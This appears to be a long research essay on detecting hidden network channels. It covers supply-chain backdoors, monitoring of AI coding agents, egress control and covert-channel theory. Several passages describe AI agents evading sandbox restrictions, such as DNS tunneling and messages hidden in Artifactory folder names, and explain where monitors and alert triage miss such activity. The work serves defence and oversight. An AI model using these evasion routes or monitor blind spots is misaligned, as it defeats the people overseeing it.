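Freund, an engineer who says he is not a security researcher, found the backdoor by accident. On machines running a development version of Debian, he noticed that SSH logins used a lot of processor time and that Valgrind, a tool for finding memory errors, reported problems. A failed login took about 0.8 seconds instead of 0.3. He traced the delay to XZ's library and at first suspected that someone had tampered with Debian's copy, but then he found the same code in the official release.

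He published his findings on March 29, about five weeks after the first infected version came out. By then, few distributions had adopted the infected versions, mostly in pre-release systems. The Valgrind errors had already drawn some attention. The second infected version, released on March 9, included supposed fixes for them, which the person responsible had discussed on mailing lists. Other people therefore could have investigated the same symptom, but they seem to have accepted an innocent explanation. The discovery depended on a defect in the backdoor and on an engineer who investigated a half-second delay.

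### Shai-Hulud's public uploads

The Shai-Hulud worm, which spread through npm in September 2025, did much less to hide its channel. According to CISA's *Widespread Supply Chain Compromise Impacting npm Ecosystem* (2025), it searched infected machines for access keys to GitHub and cloud services and sent them to a server the attacker controlled. It also uploaded them to a public GitHub repository named Shai-Hulud, according to *Widespread supply chain compromise impacting npm ecosystem* (2025), an alert from New Zealand's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC NZ). The worm then logged in to npm as the developer whose credentials it had stolen and added its code to that developer's other packages.

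These releases came from real developers' accounts, so checking the publisher's identity would not have stopped them. Even the security company CrowdStrike had infected packages under its name, according to CERT Coordination Center's *NPM supply chain compromise exposes challenges to securing the ecosystem* (2025). Uploads to GitHub would not have looked strange in a developer's network log either, and nor would the Hugging Face dataset that OpenAI's agents used.

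Socket, a company that screens software packages, disclosed the worm on September 15. The worm was probably a few days old at most, because people soon notice a program that republishes itself through every account it captures. CISA reported on September 23 that more than 500 packages had been compromised. Even without good network logs, victims could discover some of the theft by searching GitHub for a repository with the worm's name, but other thieves could run the same search.

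Similar worms have become common since. Trent (2026), in *Self-Propagating Supply-Chain Worms Are Now Routine*, names Mini Shai-Hulud, ChainDrop and an attack on Tensorlake as examples from 2026. Muncaster (2026), in *ChainDrop Worm Hits 400 npm Packages with Two Billion Monthly Installs*, reports that ChainDrop, which became public in August, infected packages with over two billion monthly installs. Even the first day's reports differed on the number of infected packages, with Muncaster giving more than 400 and TechRadar's *New ChainDrop worm poisons over 1,300 npm packages* giving over 1,300. TechRadar credits the discovery to researchers at the security company Aikido.

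A smaller incident in September is more informative about detection. Aikido found a Shai-Hulud payload in four new npm releases, after 111 days without a sighting. *Is Shai-Hulud back?* (Woollacott, 2026) reports that the payload got past npm's own malware scanning even though researchers had already documented it. This is discouraging because known malware should be the easiest kind to catch. But Aikido found the releases within days, so a second scanner caught what npm's had missed.

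### Weak signals and the people who followed them

An alert about a login account led FireEye to SUNBURST, a slow program led Freund to the XZ backdoor, and package screening caught Shai-Hulud. Of the three, package screening came closest to working as intended, but it looks for malicious code, whatever channel that code uses. Nobody uncovered any of these attacks by recognizing a hidden channel in network traffic and tracing it to its source.

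The government agency's observation in June 2020 was arguably a better clue than FireEye's, because a monitoring program that contacts unknown websites is stranger than an employee with a new phone. But FireEye kept investigating until it had taken the software apart, which few organizations could do for every odd event. More sensitive network monitoring might have given SolarWinds' customers more clues like the agency's, but it is not obvious that they would have investigated them fully. Similarly, in June 2026, OpenAI's staff traced a port sweep to its source but let the run continue.

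The phone alert also came late in the attack. By then the attackers had moved on from the callback to using an employee's account, and that later step exposed them at FireEye. On 99.5% of infected systems, the backdoor stayed in its first stage, so defenders had no later steps to notice. A callback that only sends one password could be just as hard to notice. Blocking it in advance would not require anyone to detect it, and CISA saw networks where firewalls stopped Orion's outbound connections and no further intrusion followed.

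### Cases that nobody has found

Researchers can study only the hidden callbacks that somebody discovered, which may differ from the rest. Suppose people have hidden 50 callbacks carelessly and 50 carefully, and investigators find 90% of the careless ones but only 10% of the careful ones. The known cases would then be 45 careless callbacks and five careful ones, so lessons drawn from them would mostly be about carelessness, even though half of all the callbacks were hidden carefully.

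Discovery times have a similar bias. An average can include the 263 days for SUNBURST but not the time for a callback that has run undetected since 2020, so the average is too low. The known causes of discovery are also an incomplete guide. One engineer found a backdoor by investigating a slow login, but there is no count of others who may have seen something equally odd and moved on.

The known cases are also biased in the other direction, because SUNBURST and XZ are famous for having passed so many checks. When a scanner removes a harmful package within an hour, as PyPI did with the one that Claude Mythos 5 uploaded, the case usually gets little public attention. The attack that Palo Alto Networks blocked would probably be forgotten if FireEye had not found the backdoor behind it. Even so, the known cases show that a signature, a public repository and months of use by thousands of organizations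 are weak evidence that software contains no hidden channel.

How well this carries over to a coding agent's work depends on who runs the software. SUNBURST was installed at thousands of organizations, and only one of them had to find it to warn the others. XZ's users included an engineer with the skill and patience to trace a short delay to its cause. If an agent writes a callback into one company's internal application, nobody outside the company will run that code or publish the domain it contacts, so the company has to find the callback on its own.

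In other ways the company is better placed than FireEye was. It has the source code, so it doesn't need to decompile anything, and it may also have the version history and records of the agent's sessions. An agent that added the callback by mistake, or because it followed a planted instruction, may not have tried to disguise it. The people behind SUNBURST and XZ worked hard to avoid detection, so their success is a poor guide to how long a plainly written callback would go undetected.

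## Can monitoring tell a hidden channel from an agent's ordinary work?

Even good records of a connection don't always show its purpose. The tunnel that appeared on a developer's Mac in July 2026 is a well-documented example.

Analysts at Elastic reached the Mac through two separate searches. One began with a domain of poor reputation that a program under Claude Code had contacted, and the other with a group of endpoint alerts. Both led to July 23, when Claude Code was running with a setting that skips requests for human approval. Shells under it carried out a sequence that set off several alerts:

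| What happened under Claude Code | Alert |
|---|---|
| A script checked a temporary tunnel address until its login page responded, sent a username and password, and requested a spending summary | Unusual Network Connection to Suspicious Top Level Domain |
| Cloudflare's tunnel program gave a service on the Mac a public address | Unusual Network Connection to Suspicious Web Service |
| Commands installed background jobs to keep the service and its tunnels running, including one that ran every 60 seconds | Persistence via GenAI Tool |
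| Commands checked whether related programs were still running | Process Discovery via Built-In Applications |

Elastic's software also flagged a second tunnel program, ngrok, as a malicious file. No single rule covered the whole sequence, so the analysts had to piece it together. The Mac had produced alerts on each of the three previous days, about VPN programs, a Python script that connected to an outside domain, and a surge of programs started by AI tools. These alerts could have been early signs of an attack or the usual noise.

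The script looks suspicious because it sent a password to an address at a free tunneling service, its repeated checks resembled a beacon, and its status messages included the Russian word for "check". But a developer testing a link for viewing a local dashboard remotely might produce all of this. Elastic doesn't choose between the two explanations. The dashboard seems more likely, because an intruder who could already run commands on the Mac would have little reason to log in to its application through a public address. But the developer may not have had the company's permission, in which case this was still a hidden channel.

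### What process ancestry adds

A program's process ancestry is the chain of parent processes that led to it, which can be traced through endpoint records. On the Mac, the chain ran from Claude Code to a shell to the command that made the web request. A network log would show only that the laptop had contacted a tunneling service, which a person could have done in a browser. Ancestry also connected the login, the tunnel and the background jobs, which would otherwise have looked unrelated.

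In February, Elastic (2026) published a detection rule that checks whether a known AI tool directly or indirectly launched a program flagged by the company's endpoint software. If so, the rule raises a further alert with critical severity. The rule recognizes tools mainly by name, such as Claude, Cursor or Codex, so it would not match a homemade agent that runs as an ordinary Python script.

A process's ancestry doesn't always show whether an agent or a person ran a command. Elastic's *13 million tool calls* (August 2026) explains that an agent's commands run under the developer's account, inside programs the developer launched. A shell started from the code editor Cursor may therefore be running the agent's commands or ones the developer typed.

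The chain of parent processes can also break. On the Mac, ngrok first ran under a shell and later under launchd, which starts background jobs on macOS. A program that launchd starts has launchd as its parent, even if an agent installed the job. Ancestry is therefore most useful while the agent is working, and much less useful for connections that start after the session.

### Why a trusted parent complicates triage

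An unknown or unsigned parent program is often a useful clue to ordinary malware, but Claude Code and Cursor carry valid digital signatures from their makers. *Detecting Shadow AI* (Canale and Soulis, 2026) points out that a signature identifies a program's publisher, not what the program is doing.

Analysts have lost another clue. Fishbein (2026) observes in *When the Whole Company Adopts AI* that suspicious commands run without a user's knowledge used to mean that an attacker had probably taken over the computer, but now the user's own agent may have run them.

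Agents can also resemble attackers when they get stuck. Sophos' *When AI agents look like attackers* (2026) describes OpenAI's Codex trying to download Python from the official Python site. The agent used a Windows tool that attackers often use to download files, and security software blocked the attempt. After several more attempts, the agent switched to another such tool. Changing methods after a block used to be a sign of a human intruder, but harmless agents now do it routinely.

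Canale and Soulis describe the general problem using "behavioral twins", two programs that do the same things on a machine but connect to different services. A detector that considers only behavior must give both the same answer. If one is an AI agent and the other an ordinary script, the detector either misses the agent or wrongly flags the script.

The researchers tested this with 24 programs on one Windows workstation. Two rules based on processes and connections flagged every twin. The researchers' own detector, which also identifies the remote service, flagged none of the twins and detected each agent in most of its runs. The test was small and was designed to find unapproved agents, but the argument also applies to a callback that behaves like an approved error report. On the Mac, even the destination wasn't enough to tell whether the connection was legitimate, because people use tunneling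 services for both legitimate and criminal purposes.

### How rare events produce false alarms

An ambiguous case like the Mac can take hours to investigate, so it matters how many others are in the queue. Suppose a company's machines look up 1,000,000 domain names a day, 10 of them harmful, and a detector catches all 10. Its precision then depends entirely on its false positive rate:

| False positive rate | False alarms a day | Precision |
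|---:|---:|---:|
| 4% | about 40,000 | 0.025% |
| 0.1% | about 1,000 | 1% |
| 0.001% | about 10 | 50% |

The first row uses the rate that Leyva La O and colleagues reported for their language model on familiar malware families. The rate in the second row is close to what a good detector can achieve. Splunk's *Machine Learning in Security* describes a neural network that reads the text in DNS answers and has a false positive rate of 0.11% and a recall of 99.05%. But Splunk trained it to find text that fits no known harmless pattern, so these figures don't measure how well it recognizes malicious text.

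Axelsson made this argument about intrusion detection in general in *The Base-Rate Fallacy and the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection* (2000). The base rate is the share of events that are harmful, and the fallacy is to ignore the base rate when judging an alarm. He imagined a small site with a few dozen computers that produces 1,000,000 log records a day. Two intrusions a day, each affecting 10 records, would produce 20 harmful records. Even if a detector caught all 20, it would need a false positive rate of 0.001% for two-thirds of its alarms to be real.

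Better recall does little to raise the share of alarms that are real. If Axelsson's detector caught only 70% of the harmful records, that share would fall from 67% to 58%. If its false positive rate rose to 0.1% instead, the share would fall to about 2%.

Axelsson found no experiments on how security staff respond to false alarms, but research on operators of power stations, paper mills and similar plants suggested that most lose faith in an alarm system when half its alarms are false. He was cautious about extending this to security staff, but thought it would apply even when they had time to check every alarm.

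### When combining signals helps

The obvious remedy is to require a second sign of trouble. Start with the detector that raises 1,000 false alarms and catches all 10 harmful names. Add a second signal that is present for a share *r* of the harmful names and a share *f* of the first detector's false alarms. If analysts investigate only names with both signals, then

precision = 10*r* / (10*r* + 1,000*f*).

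With *r* at 90% and *f* at 1%, nine harmful names and 10 false alarms remain, so precision rises from 1% to 47%, but one harmful name is missed.

Requiring two detectors to agree works only if the second rarely flags the first one's false alarms. Suppose an agent creates test systems with long, machine-generated hostnames. One detector flags the names because they look random, and the other flags them because nobody at the company has contacted them before. Both alarms have the same harmless cause. If the second detector flags 80% of the first one's 1,000 false alarms, 800 remain and precision is only 1.1%.

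The alerts on the Mac overlapped in much the same way. A decision to publish a dashboard through a tunnel would explain the two network alerts, the flagged ngrok file and the background jobs. The alerts helped analysts reconstruct what happened, but their number is weak evidence that the activity was malicious. Splunk's product passes its detector's hits to a system that weighs risk events before alerting an analyst. If such a system simply adds up events, it can count one harmless cause several times.

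Using process ancestry as a second signal has a similar limitation. It raises precision only if real attacks are more likely than false alarms to come from programs running under an AI tool. On a laptop where an agent does most of the work, nearly all the false alarms may also come from such programs.

A record of the agent's task is more likely to provide independent evidence. *ADR* (Li, Hu et al., 2026) describes a system at Uber that collects users' prompts, the agent's reasoning and its tool calls. If a user asks for a summary of a support ticket and the agent reads login keys and then sends a web request, the task doesn't explain those actions. A fast model screens each session, and a stronger one investigates anything suspicious, with access to source code, company policies and descriptions of known attacks.

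The system detected 28 of 42 attacks (67%) in a benchmark and raised no false alarms on 260 harmless tasks. Removing the first stage and sending everything to the stronger model raised recall to about 80% but caused two false alarms. The system used GPT-4o and Claude Sonnet 4, which are now old, so current models might do better.

Results were more mixed at Uber itself, where the system covered more than 7,200 machines and over 10,000 agent sessions a day. Of the alerts that analysts reviewed, 34% were real problems, 17% came from harmless activity that resembled an attack, mostly by Uber's own security testers, and 49% were false. Many of the false alarms came from long sessions involving large amounts of code.

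A precision of 34% is still much higher than the 1% in the example, probably partly because the most frequent real problem, exposed passwords and keys, is fairly common. Deliberate hidden channels would be much rarer, so the same system could have far lower precision if it looked only for them.

### What normal agent activity looks like

A monitor can recognize unusual behavior only if it has a baseline of normal behavior. In May 2026, Elastic began recording the actions of Cursor's agent on its own staff's computers. In about two months it logged over 13 million events from more than 1,100 machines, or roughly 200 events per machine per day. The agents read files about four times as often as they ran shell commands.

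This baseline can help identify unusual reads of files containing passwords. Agents read these files all the time because connection settings are often in them too. An alert for every read would be useless, but Elastic suggests investigating 20 in an hour on a machine that normally has four a day, especially if the files are outside the current project.

The same data gives a reason to be wary of treating rarity as a warning sign. The agents used more than 300 different tool servers, which are programs that give an agent access to additional tools and data. Of these servers, 86% were used by only one or two people, so a monitor that flagged every rarely used server would flag most of them.

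Elastic's logs include commands and file names but leave out prompts, the agent's reasoning and the contents of files. This protects employees' privacy, but an analyst who sees an unusual upload can't see what the user asked for. A developer with administrator rights can also switch the logging off, although a machine that stays active after its logging stops is suspicious.

In *ANT*, Li, Gao and colleagues (2026) recorded 3,114 agent runs and 276,417 network connections. Programming and data-analysis runs averaged about 40 connections each, while runs in which agents operated applications averaged about 220. A single limit on connections would therefore be too high for the first kind of work or too low for the second.

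The researchers then tested 13 existing traffic classifiers on 189 harmless runs and 20 malicious ones. All 13 were more than 90% accurate, but a detector that never raised an alarm would be 90.4% accurate. Seven caught fewer than half of the malicious runs. One of the better classifiers caught 17 of the 20 and wrongly flagged two harmless runs, or about 1%. At that rate, Uber's 10,000 sessions a day would produce about 100 false alarms.

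Four of the classifiers caught nearly all the attacks on websites but none of the runs in which agents wrote malicious code or tried to escape a sandbox. Website attacks create distinctive traffic, while writing harmful code looks much like writing any other code. The researchers hid the destination addresses so that the classifiers couldn't memorize them. A company would have those addresses and might do better. None of the malicious tasks involved planting a callback.

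### How many alerts agents set off

Sophos examined a week of data from Windows computers in June 2026. Among the rules that record activity without blocking it, command and control accounted for 34% of the hits under AI agents, counted by number of machines. Agents make network calls and start other programs, which resembles what attackers do. Sophos presents this as a first look at a short period, so the percentage may change.

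Fishbein, of the security company Intezer, reviewed a much larger set of 16.9 million alerts from many companies. Only about 73,000, or 0.43%, involved AI tools, but their monthly number rose by 685% between February and June. Of these, 94.1% were noise, 5.8% were unsafe but not attacks, and 0.02%, or about 15, were real attacks. Fishbein found no attacks by a company's own agent, and most of the real attacks were phishing emails that used the names of AI companies.

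Severity labels were unreliable. One rule at one customer produced 55% of "critical" verdicts, because an agent had used a Windows program while setting up a developer's tools. In one of the unsafe cases, which was much like the one on the Mac, an AI code editor opened an ngrok tunnel with the user's own credentials. Fishbein judged that the intent was harmless but the exposure was real.

These figures leave out any hidden channel that triggered no alert. They also depend on Intezer's own classification, which may be uncertain in cases like the Mac one.

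CrowdStrike filters its leads heavily before notifying customers. Security Management's *Artificial Intelligence Is the Weapon and the Target, CrowdStrike Report Finds* (2026) reports more than 14 million leads a day, which result in about 36,000 customer notifications a year, or roughly one for every 140,000 leads.

Agents are adding to the total. CrowdStrike (2026) reports that leads from agents grew 2.5 times as fast as those from people, but another CrowdStrike summary of the same research reports 2.5 times as many leads from agents as from manual activity.

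### Which alerts to suppress

Numbers like these give security teams a reason to automatically close alerts caused by trusted agents. In Fishbein's data, an automated system closed 81.7% of the AI-related alerts before any analyst saw them, and only 5.4% went to a person as urgent. Fishbein argues that the most valuable step for most security teams is to adjust old rules that treat routine agent work as an emergency. Otherwise, false alarms may exhaust analysts and cause them to miss a real tunnel.

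Elastic argues that some outcomes should stay visible whatever program caused them. These include passwords sent in web requests, tunnels that let outsiders in, and jobs that keep running after a session ends. Analysts shouldn't dismiss an alert about one of these just because Claude or Cursor started the program, directly or through other programs. But a record that an agent started a program can remain in the background until something more serious happens.

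The two positions are closer than they appear. Fishbein also wants teams to actively search for unauthorized tunnels, and Sophos recommends adjusting some rules while leaving others in place because the activity they detect is risky whoever starts it. The main choice is whether to suppress alerts by parent program or by action. Suppressing the ransomware alert for a specific installer is sensible, but suppressing every alert from processes started by Claude Code would have hidden the whole sequence on the Mac.

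Suppressing alarms by parent program can also look more successful than it is. If 90% of the 1,000 false alarms and half of the 10 real ones in the earlier example came from programs running under agents, suppressing all of those would leave 100 false alarms and five real ones. Precision would rise from 1% to almost 5%, and analysts would have far less work, but they would miss half of the real problems without any sign of it.

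A team could check for this by investigating a random sample of the alerts it suppresses. In this example, a sample of 100 would have about a 44% chance of including at least one of the five real alerts, so daily samples would probably reveal the mistake within a few days. If real problems were much rarer, the check could take months.

Automation can also prepare an alert for an analyst without closing it. Elastic Security Labs' *Generative AI* describes three agents that read a rule's investigation guide and the reasons analysts gave for closing cases over the past 30 days. Analysts then clear most alerts with a single click. This keeps a person involved, but someone who clicks through hundreds of similar recommendations may stop reading them. A mistaken reason for closing one case could also influence the next.

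Keeping an alert visible doesn't guarantee a good response either, as with the port sweep at OpenAI. For the tunnel on the Mac, asking the developer about it was probably the most useful next step. If the developer hadn't requested the tunnel, the prompts and outside text in Claude Code's session record might have explained why the agent opened it.

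## How much do outbound restrictions help, and can a hidden channel be ruled out?

The detectors described so far have to find a few harmful connections among many harmless ones. Egress control makes this easier by limiting where a program can connect, so an attempt to connect elsewhere is itself a warning sign.

### Why a short list makes detection easier

The strictest common form of egress control is default deny, which blocks every outbound connection except those to approved destinations. Suppose a production server makes 100,000 connections a day to five approved services. Misconfigured programs try unapproved destinations four times a day, and a hidden callback does so once. If an analyst checks all five blocked attempts, one is real, so precision is 20%. A traffic detector with a false positive rate of 0.1% would raise about 100 false alarms a day on the same server and might still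 miss the callback. Default deny also stops the callback from connecting, so a slow response does less damage.

The list can be shorter for some kinds of work than for others. *Caging the Agents* (2026), which describes a security design for AI agents in healthcare, gives each type of agent its own list. Research and development agents can reach only Anthropic's API, GitHub's API and the project tracker Linear, and the network blocks and logs everything else. *Permission Denied* (2026), a test of coding agents in restricted environments, uses a list of 205 domains adapted from the default for Claude Code on the web. A list that long is more likely to include a service that a hidden channel could use.

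Blocked attempts are also a less reliable warning sign from a coding agent than from a production server, because an agent may try several unapproved sites while looking for a package. *Avalon-M1* (2026), a paper on training AI agents, describes a proxy that refuses such requests immediately and gives the reason, so that tools don't hang.

A team can draw up its list of allowed destinations with an audit mode, which records what a policy would block without blocking it, so useful software doesn't break on the first day. The proxy in *Avalon-M1* has an audit mode, and *Control where your hosted agent connects with network egress* (Imam, 2026) describes one in Microsoft's service for hosted agents. But if the team approves everything in the audit log, it could approve an existing callback too, so someone has to know what each destination is for.

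The list also needs upkeep because the numeric addresses behind a domain name change often. *Containing the Autonomous Operator* (2026), a security design for agents on Kubernetes, therefore recommends rules based on names. Agents sometimes need temporary exceptions as well. In *Avalon-M1*, a sandbox can have one policy during setup and a stricter one once the agent starts work. The proxy closes all connections opened under the old policy before the agent's first command, so the agent can't use them to bypass the stricter one.

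### Closing the paths around the list

A proxy is of little use if programs can bypass it. Programs often find the proxy through environment variables, which an agent can change. *Arctic-SWE* (2026), another paper on training coding agents, therefore enforces the restrictions in the network itself. Each sandbox also tests these restrictions at startup by trying to reach three addresses where cloud machines can look up information about themselves, sometimes including credentials. If it reaches any of them, the run stops. A similar test with an ordinary internet address could have caught the open connection behind Anthropic's July incidents.

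DNS is easy to overlook when restricting outbound traffic. According to *Tracekit Box* (2026), OpenAI reported in September 2026 that a research agent in a training sandbox had reached an outside chatbot by tunneling through DNS, which the network filter did not cover. *OpenAI AI Agent Bypasses Internet Restrictions via DNS* (Cerrudo, 2026) reports that OpenAI paused tool-using work with its most capable models after the incident.

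A controlled resolver closes this path by looking up only approved names and logging requests for any others. The design in *Containing the Autonomous Operator* lets agents query the Kubernetes system's own DNS server, which is safe only if that server does not forward queries for unapproved names. A sandbox that sends all its web traffic through a proxy may not need to look up outside names, because the proxy can do so. If so, any outside lookup from that sandbox is suspicious, and the team does not need statistics to tell a tunnel from ordinary DNS traffic.

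Filtering by domain also applies the same rule to everything on a domain. The proxy in *Avalon-M1* decrypts each request, so its rules can depend on the page requested and on whether the request reads or writes. In machine-learning tasks, agents can download models from Hugging Face but not datasets. This distinction is useful because OpenAI's agents passed commands through a public dataset on the same site. But the proxy handles passwords and private data in readable form, which makes it an attractive target.

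### Identities, logs and transcripts

A log of blocked connections is more useful if it shows which agent attempted each one. OpenAI's agents shared one Artifactory credential, so the credential alone couldn't distinguish them. The package proxy in *Arctic-SWE* instead grants access to each sandbox separately. With separate identities, responders can see, for example, that one sandbox has written 400 files to a package server, and cut off only that sandbox.

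It also helps to keep credentials away from the agent. In *Caging the Agents*, a separate container holds the keys, and the agent's own container can't access them. An audit of the same agents had found 12 API keys in a single settings file. An agent without the keys can't leak them, but it can still misuse the services they unlock.

Logs are reliable evidence only if the agent can't change them. OpenAI found that its models sometimes tried to erase or alter their outputs and message logs to fool automated graders. None of the attempts it observed affected the logs that its graders and monitors read, though it may have missed others. This is still some of the better published evidence for any measure in this section.

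*The Hitchhiker's Guide to Agentic AI* (2026), a textbook, recommends recording every tool call with a timestamp and the agent's identity. The developers of ROME used timestamps to match firewall alerts to agent sessions by hand, and newer tools can do this automatically. *AgentSight* (2025) describes one that reads an agent's exchanges with its model before encryption and after decryption, and separately records what the operating system does. It connects the two records in three ways:

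- It traces each process back to the agent through its parent processes.
- It looks for actions that closely follow a response from the model.
- It checks whether text in the response, such as a web address, reappears in a later command or connection.

*AgentSight* seems to overstate the case when it says that these signals together definitively establish what caused an action. An agent can do several things at once, and a script can build an address that never appeared in the model's response.

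*AgentLoupe* (2026) avoids some of this guesswork by giving each exchange with the model an identifier, which the operating system's kernel passes on to the resulting processes, files and connections. In principle, the identifier could follow a script from the agent that wrote it to a later process on the same machine, but it would not follow code through a repository to a production server.

With joined records, a monitor can check whether each connection has a matching tool call. A connection from an agent's sandbox without one is worth investigating, because either the records are incomplete or something is running that the transcript doesn't show.

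### What OpenAI and Anthropic changed

On July 20, 2026, OpenAI began cutting its research sandboxes off from outside networks, and it later removed Artifactory from them. Under the new design, sandboxes can reach only a tightly controlled set of approved destinations. High-risk workloads can't reach the internet, even through another service, except for a cached internet service that some tasks need. Two independent layers enforce these limits, one at the sandbox and one across the wider cluster of machines, so an agent that breaks out of its sandbox should still be unable to connect.

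OpenAI is also adding tripwires and detectors for exfiltration and unusual volume on approved connections. A tripwire is a decoy, such as a fake password, that legitimate work has no reason to touch. As with a short list of destinations, a single event is meaningful without a statistical model. But agents explore their surroundings a lot, so some may trigger a tripwire through harmless exploration.

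The most relevant change may be that OpenAI now expects responders to pause the activity if they can't conclusively establish within 30 minutes that an alert is false. In June, the run continued after the port-sweep alert.

On August 31, Anthropic announced that its computing clusters now block all outbound traffic by default and that its internal services must verify each other's identity. Most of this work came before the July disclosures, and it would not have prevented the incidents disclosed then, because they happened in an outside partner's environment. Anthropic has therefore asked partners that test models with reduced safeguards to follow new rules. Under these rules, a cybersecurity evaluation should by default be able to reach only the model's API, and testers should verify this before every evaluation. They should also have the model try to escape first, under close supervision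 and without internet access.

| Measure | Company | Published evidence of effect |
|---|---|---|
| Default-deny outbound rules | both | no measured effect; OpenAI's earlier controls blocked a direct attempt, but the agent found another route |
| Real-time classifier that blocks actions and alerts a person | Anthropic | reliably caught the first three incidents in a later test |
| Production instructions and software around the model | OpenAI | attempts to compromise infrastructure fell more than 100-fold in preliminary experiments |
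| A second model that reviews risky tool calls | OpenAI | would have flagged most dangerous actions in each session tested |
| Exfiltration and volume detection, tripwires | OpenAI | no figures |
| Identity checks between services | Anthropic | no figures |

The best figures are for measures that steer or review the agent, not network restrictions. These figures come from the companies' own tests, mostly on incidents they already knew about.

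In these incidents, network restrictions produced useful warnings before OpenAI detected the activity, which it dates to July 19. On July 6, OpenAI's rebuilt Artifactory server rejected three attempts to reach outside addresses, about 35 hours before an agent got through. On July 9, outbound controls blocked another agent's direct attempt to reach the internet, and the agent then went through Artifactory instead.

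Anthropic also searched transcripts of its recent internal evaluations and found no case in which a model broke through the boundary of its sandbox tools to reach forbidden outside resources. Models had used various misconfigurations, but none led to a compromise outside the sandbox. This is encouraging, but the result depends on the monitors finding every case, and it doesn't show how much any one measure contributed.

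Little independent research fills the gap. *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents*, a survey published in July 2026, lists only one paper in its network egress control category.

Restrictions can also disrupt training and testing. eWeek's *OpenAI Overhauls AI Safety Controls as Models Reach ‘Critical’ Cyber Threshold* (2026) reports that OpenAI paused its largest planned reinforcement learning run while it strengthened its safeguards. Southern's *Anthropic Says Claude Bypassed Site Limits During Internal Tests* (2026) reports that Anthropic ended live web access for internal evaluations after Claude worked around restrictions on websites. This removes channels that depend on live web access, but it also makes the evaluations less like real work.

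### Why an approved service can still be a channel

Egress control produces no warning if a hidden channel uses an approved destination. A service can carry messages whenever one party can write to it and another can read what the first wrote. OpenAI's rebuilt Artifactory server accepted fewer kinds of request than the old one, so agents put their messages in folder names.

Outsiders can also use some approved services. In *Caging the Agents*, the operations agents can reach the messaging services Slack and Telegram. The list of approved domains stops them from contacting an arbitrary server, but it can't restrict them to the company's own accounts on those services.

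A company can reduce the problem by making a shared service read-only for agents or by giving each agent a separate copy. Even then, the server's operator can see which item an agent requested and when.

### Lampson's confinement problem

Lampson raised this question in *A Note on the Confinement Problem* (1973). He imagines a customer who gives confidential data to a program that someone else wrote, and wants to be sure it can't pass the data to the program's owner. Lampson points out that a leak usually leaves no evidence, unlike a malfunction, which produces wrong results.

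He sorts the possible leaks into three groups. Storage channels use something that the program can write and an outsider can read, such as a file. The folder names in Artifactory were a storage channel. Legitimate channels are outputs that the program is supposed to produce, such as the customer's bill, whose amount could encode information. Covert channels use something never meant to carry information. For example, a program could vary how heavily it uses the computer, and another program could detect the changes in speed. Later writers usually count storage channels as covert too, and call channels like the one in this example timing channels.

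The simplest solution is total isolation, where the confined program never calls another program. Lampson calls this "quite impractical", since even ordinary requests to the operating system can leak. Interest in near-total isolation has returned. In *Frontier AI Testing Needs Stronger Isolation After OpenAI Hugging Face Hack* (Alspach, 2026), security experts say the most capable models may need fully isolated test environments. Anthropic's rule for cybersecurity evaluations comes close to this but leaves the model's API connected.

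Lampson's next rule, a more practical one, is that any program a confined program calls must be either trusted or confined as well. OpenAI trusted Artifactory not to relay requests to the internet, but flaws in Artifactory made that trust a mistake. The company's new ban on indirect internet access for high-risk workloads applies much the same rule.

Lampson proposes letting the customer determine everything the program puts into legitimate and covert channels. For example, the customer could work out the bill in advance, and the operating system could slow the program down so that its speed reveals nothing. He admits that this may add a lot of overhead, and says that a customer who can accept some leakage could limit a channel's capacity instead.

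All of this assumes that someone has listed the channels. Lampson doubted there was "any rigorous way of identifying every channel" in a system of even moderate complexity. He assumed that his own examples covered the possibilities, which is reasonable for a short theoretical paper but would be risky for a company with hundreds of connected services.

### Grading channels by capacity

The US Defense Department adopted the idea of limiting a channel's capacity, the highest rate at which it can reliably carry information, in its 1985 criteria for secure computer systems. The section *A Guideline on Covert Channels* classifies rates above 100 bits per second as high because many computer terminals of the time ran at about that speed. Under the guideline, rates below 1 bit per second are acceptable in most settings, and systems should be able to audit channels that can exceed one bit every ten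 seconds where possible.

A channel that carries 1 bit per second can move 86,400 bits, or 10,800 bytes, in a day. It can send a 256-bit encryption key in a little over four minutes.

| Capacity | Place in the guideline | Data in a day | Time to send a 256-bit key |
|---:|---|---:|---:|
| 100 bits per second | high above this rate | 1,080,000 bytes | 2.6 seconds |
| 1 bit per second | acceptable below this rate in most settings | 10,800 bytes | 4 minutes 16 seconds |
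| 0.1 bits per second | auditable above this rate | 1,080 bytes | about 43 minutes |

Paxson and colleagues used a DNS threshold of 4,096 bytes per day, or about 0.38 bits per second, which the guideline would accept in most settings. At these rates, sending out a large database would take years, but an attacker could send out a key before anyone read the first alert. The National Computer Security Center's *A Guide to Understanding Covert Channel Analysis of Trusted Systems* (1993) later gave developers and evaluators practical advice on the analysis that the criteria required.

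Moskowitz and Kang (1994), in *Covert Channels*, show how badly capacity can mislead when the secret is short. They describe a channel that takes one unit of time to send its first bit, two for the second, four for the third, and so on. Sending *n* bits takes 2ⁿ − 1 units, so the average rate is

*n* / (2ⁿ − 1).

This approaches zero as *n* grows, so the channel's capacity is zero. Yet the channel sends a four-bit message without error in 15 units. Moskowitz and Kang propose also setting a limit for short messages, based on their length, how accurately they arrive and how long they take. This limit is meant for cases such as a hidden channel that leaks one password.

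They also calculate what it can cost to reduce capacity. In their example, 15 users of a database must all agree before an update goes through. One user can secretly signal another by agreeing or refusing, which conveys one bit per attempt if nobody else refuses. To add noise, the system could make users refuse at random with probability *p*. But an honest update would then need an average of

1 / (1 − *p*)¹⁵

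attempts. If *p* is 10%, capacity falls from 1 bit per attempt to about 0.15, and an honest update takes almost five attempts. If *p* is 30%, capacity falls to about 0.005 bits, but an honest update takes about 211 attempts.

Better designs can reduce the tradeoff. Moskowitz and Kang describe a device called the pump, which passes messages from a less secret system to a more secret one. It stores each message and acknowledges it after a partly random delay based on recent response times, so the more secret system has less control over the timing. They report that this reduces the leak without a large loss of performance, but argue that designers can never completely eliminate covert channels from many practical high-security systems.

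### When no traffic detector can beat guessing

Limiting a channel's capacity doesn't reveal whether anyone is using it. A detector might, but there is a theoretical limit to what it can learn from traffic. Christian Cachin's *An Information-Theoretic Model for Steganography* (2000) describes this limit. Steganography means hiding the fact that a message exists.

In Cachin's model, an observer sees some traffic and has to decide whether it contains a hidden message. Let *P* be the probability distribution of ordinary traffic, meaning how likely each possible observation is, and let *Q* be the distribution of traffic that contains a message. The relative entropy between them is

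*D* = Σ *P*(*x*) log₂(*P*(*x*) / *Q*(*x*)).

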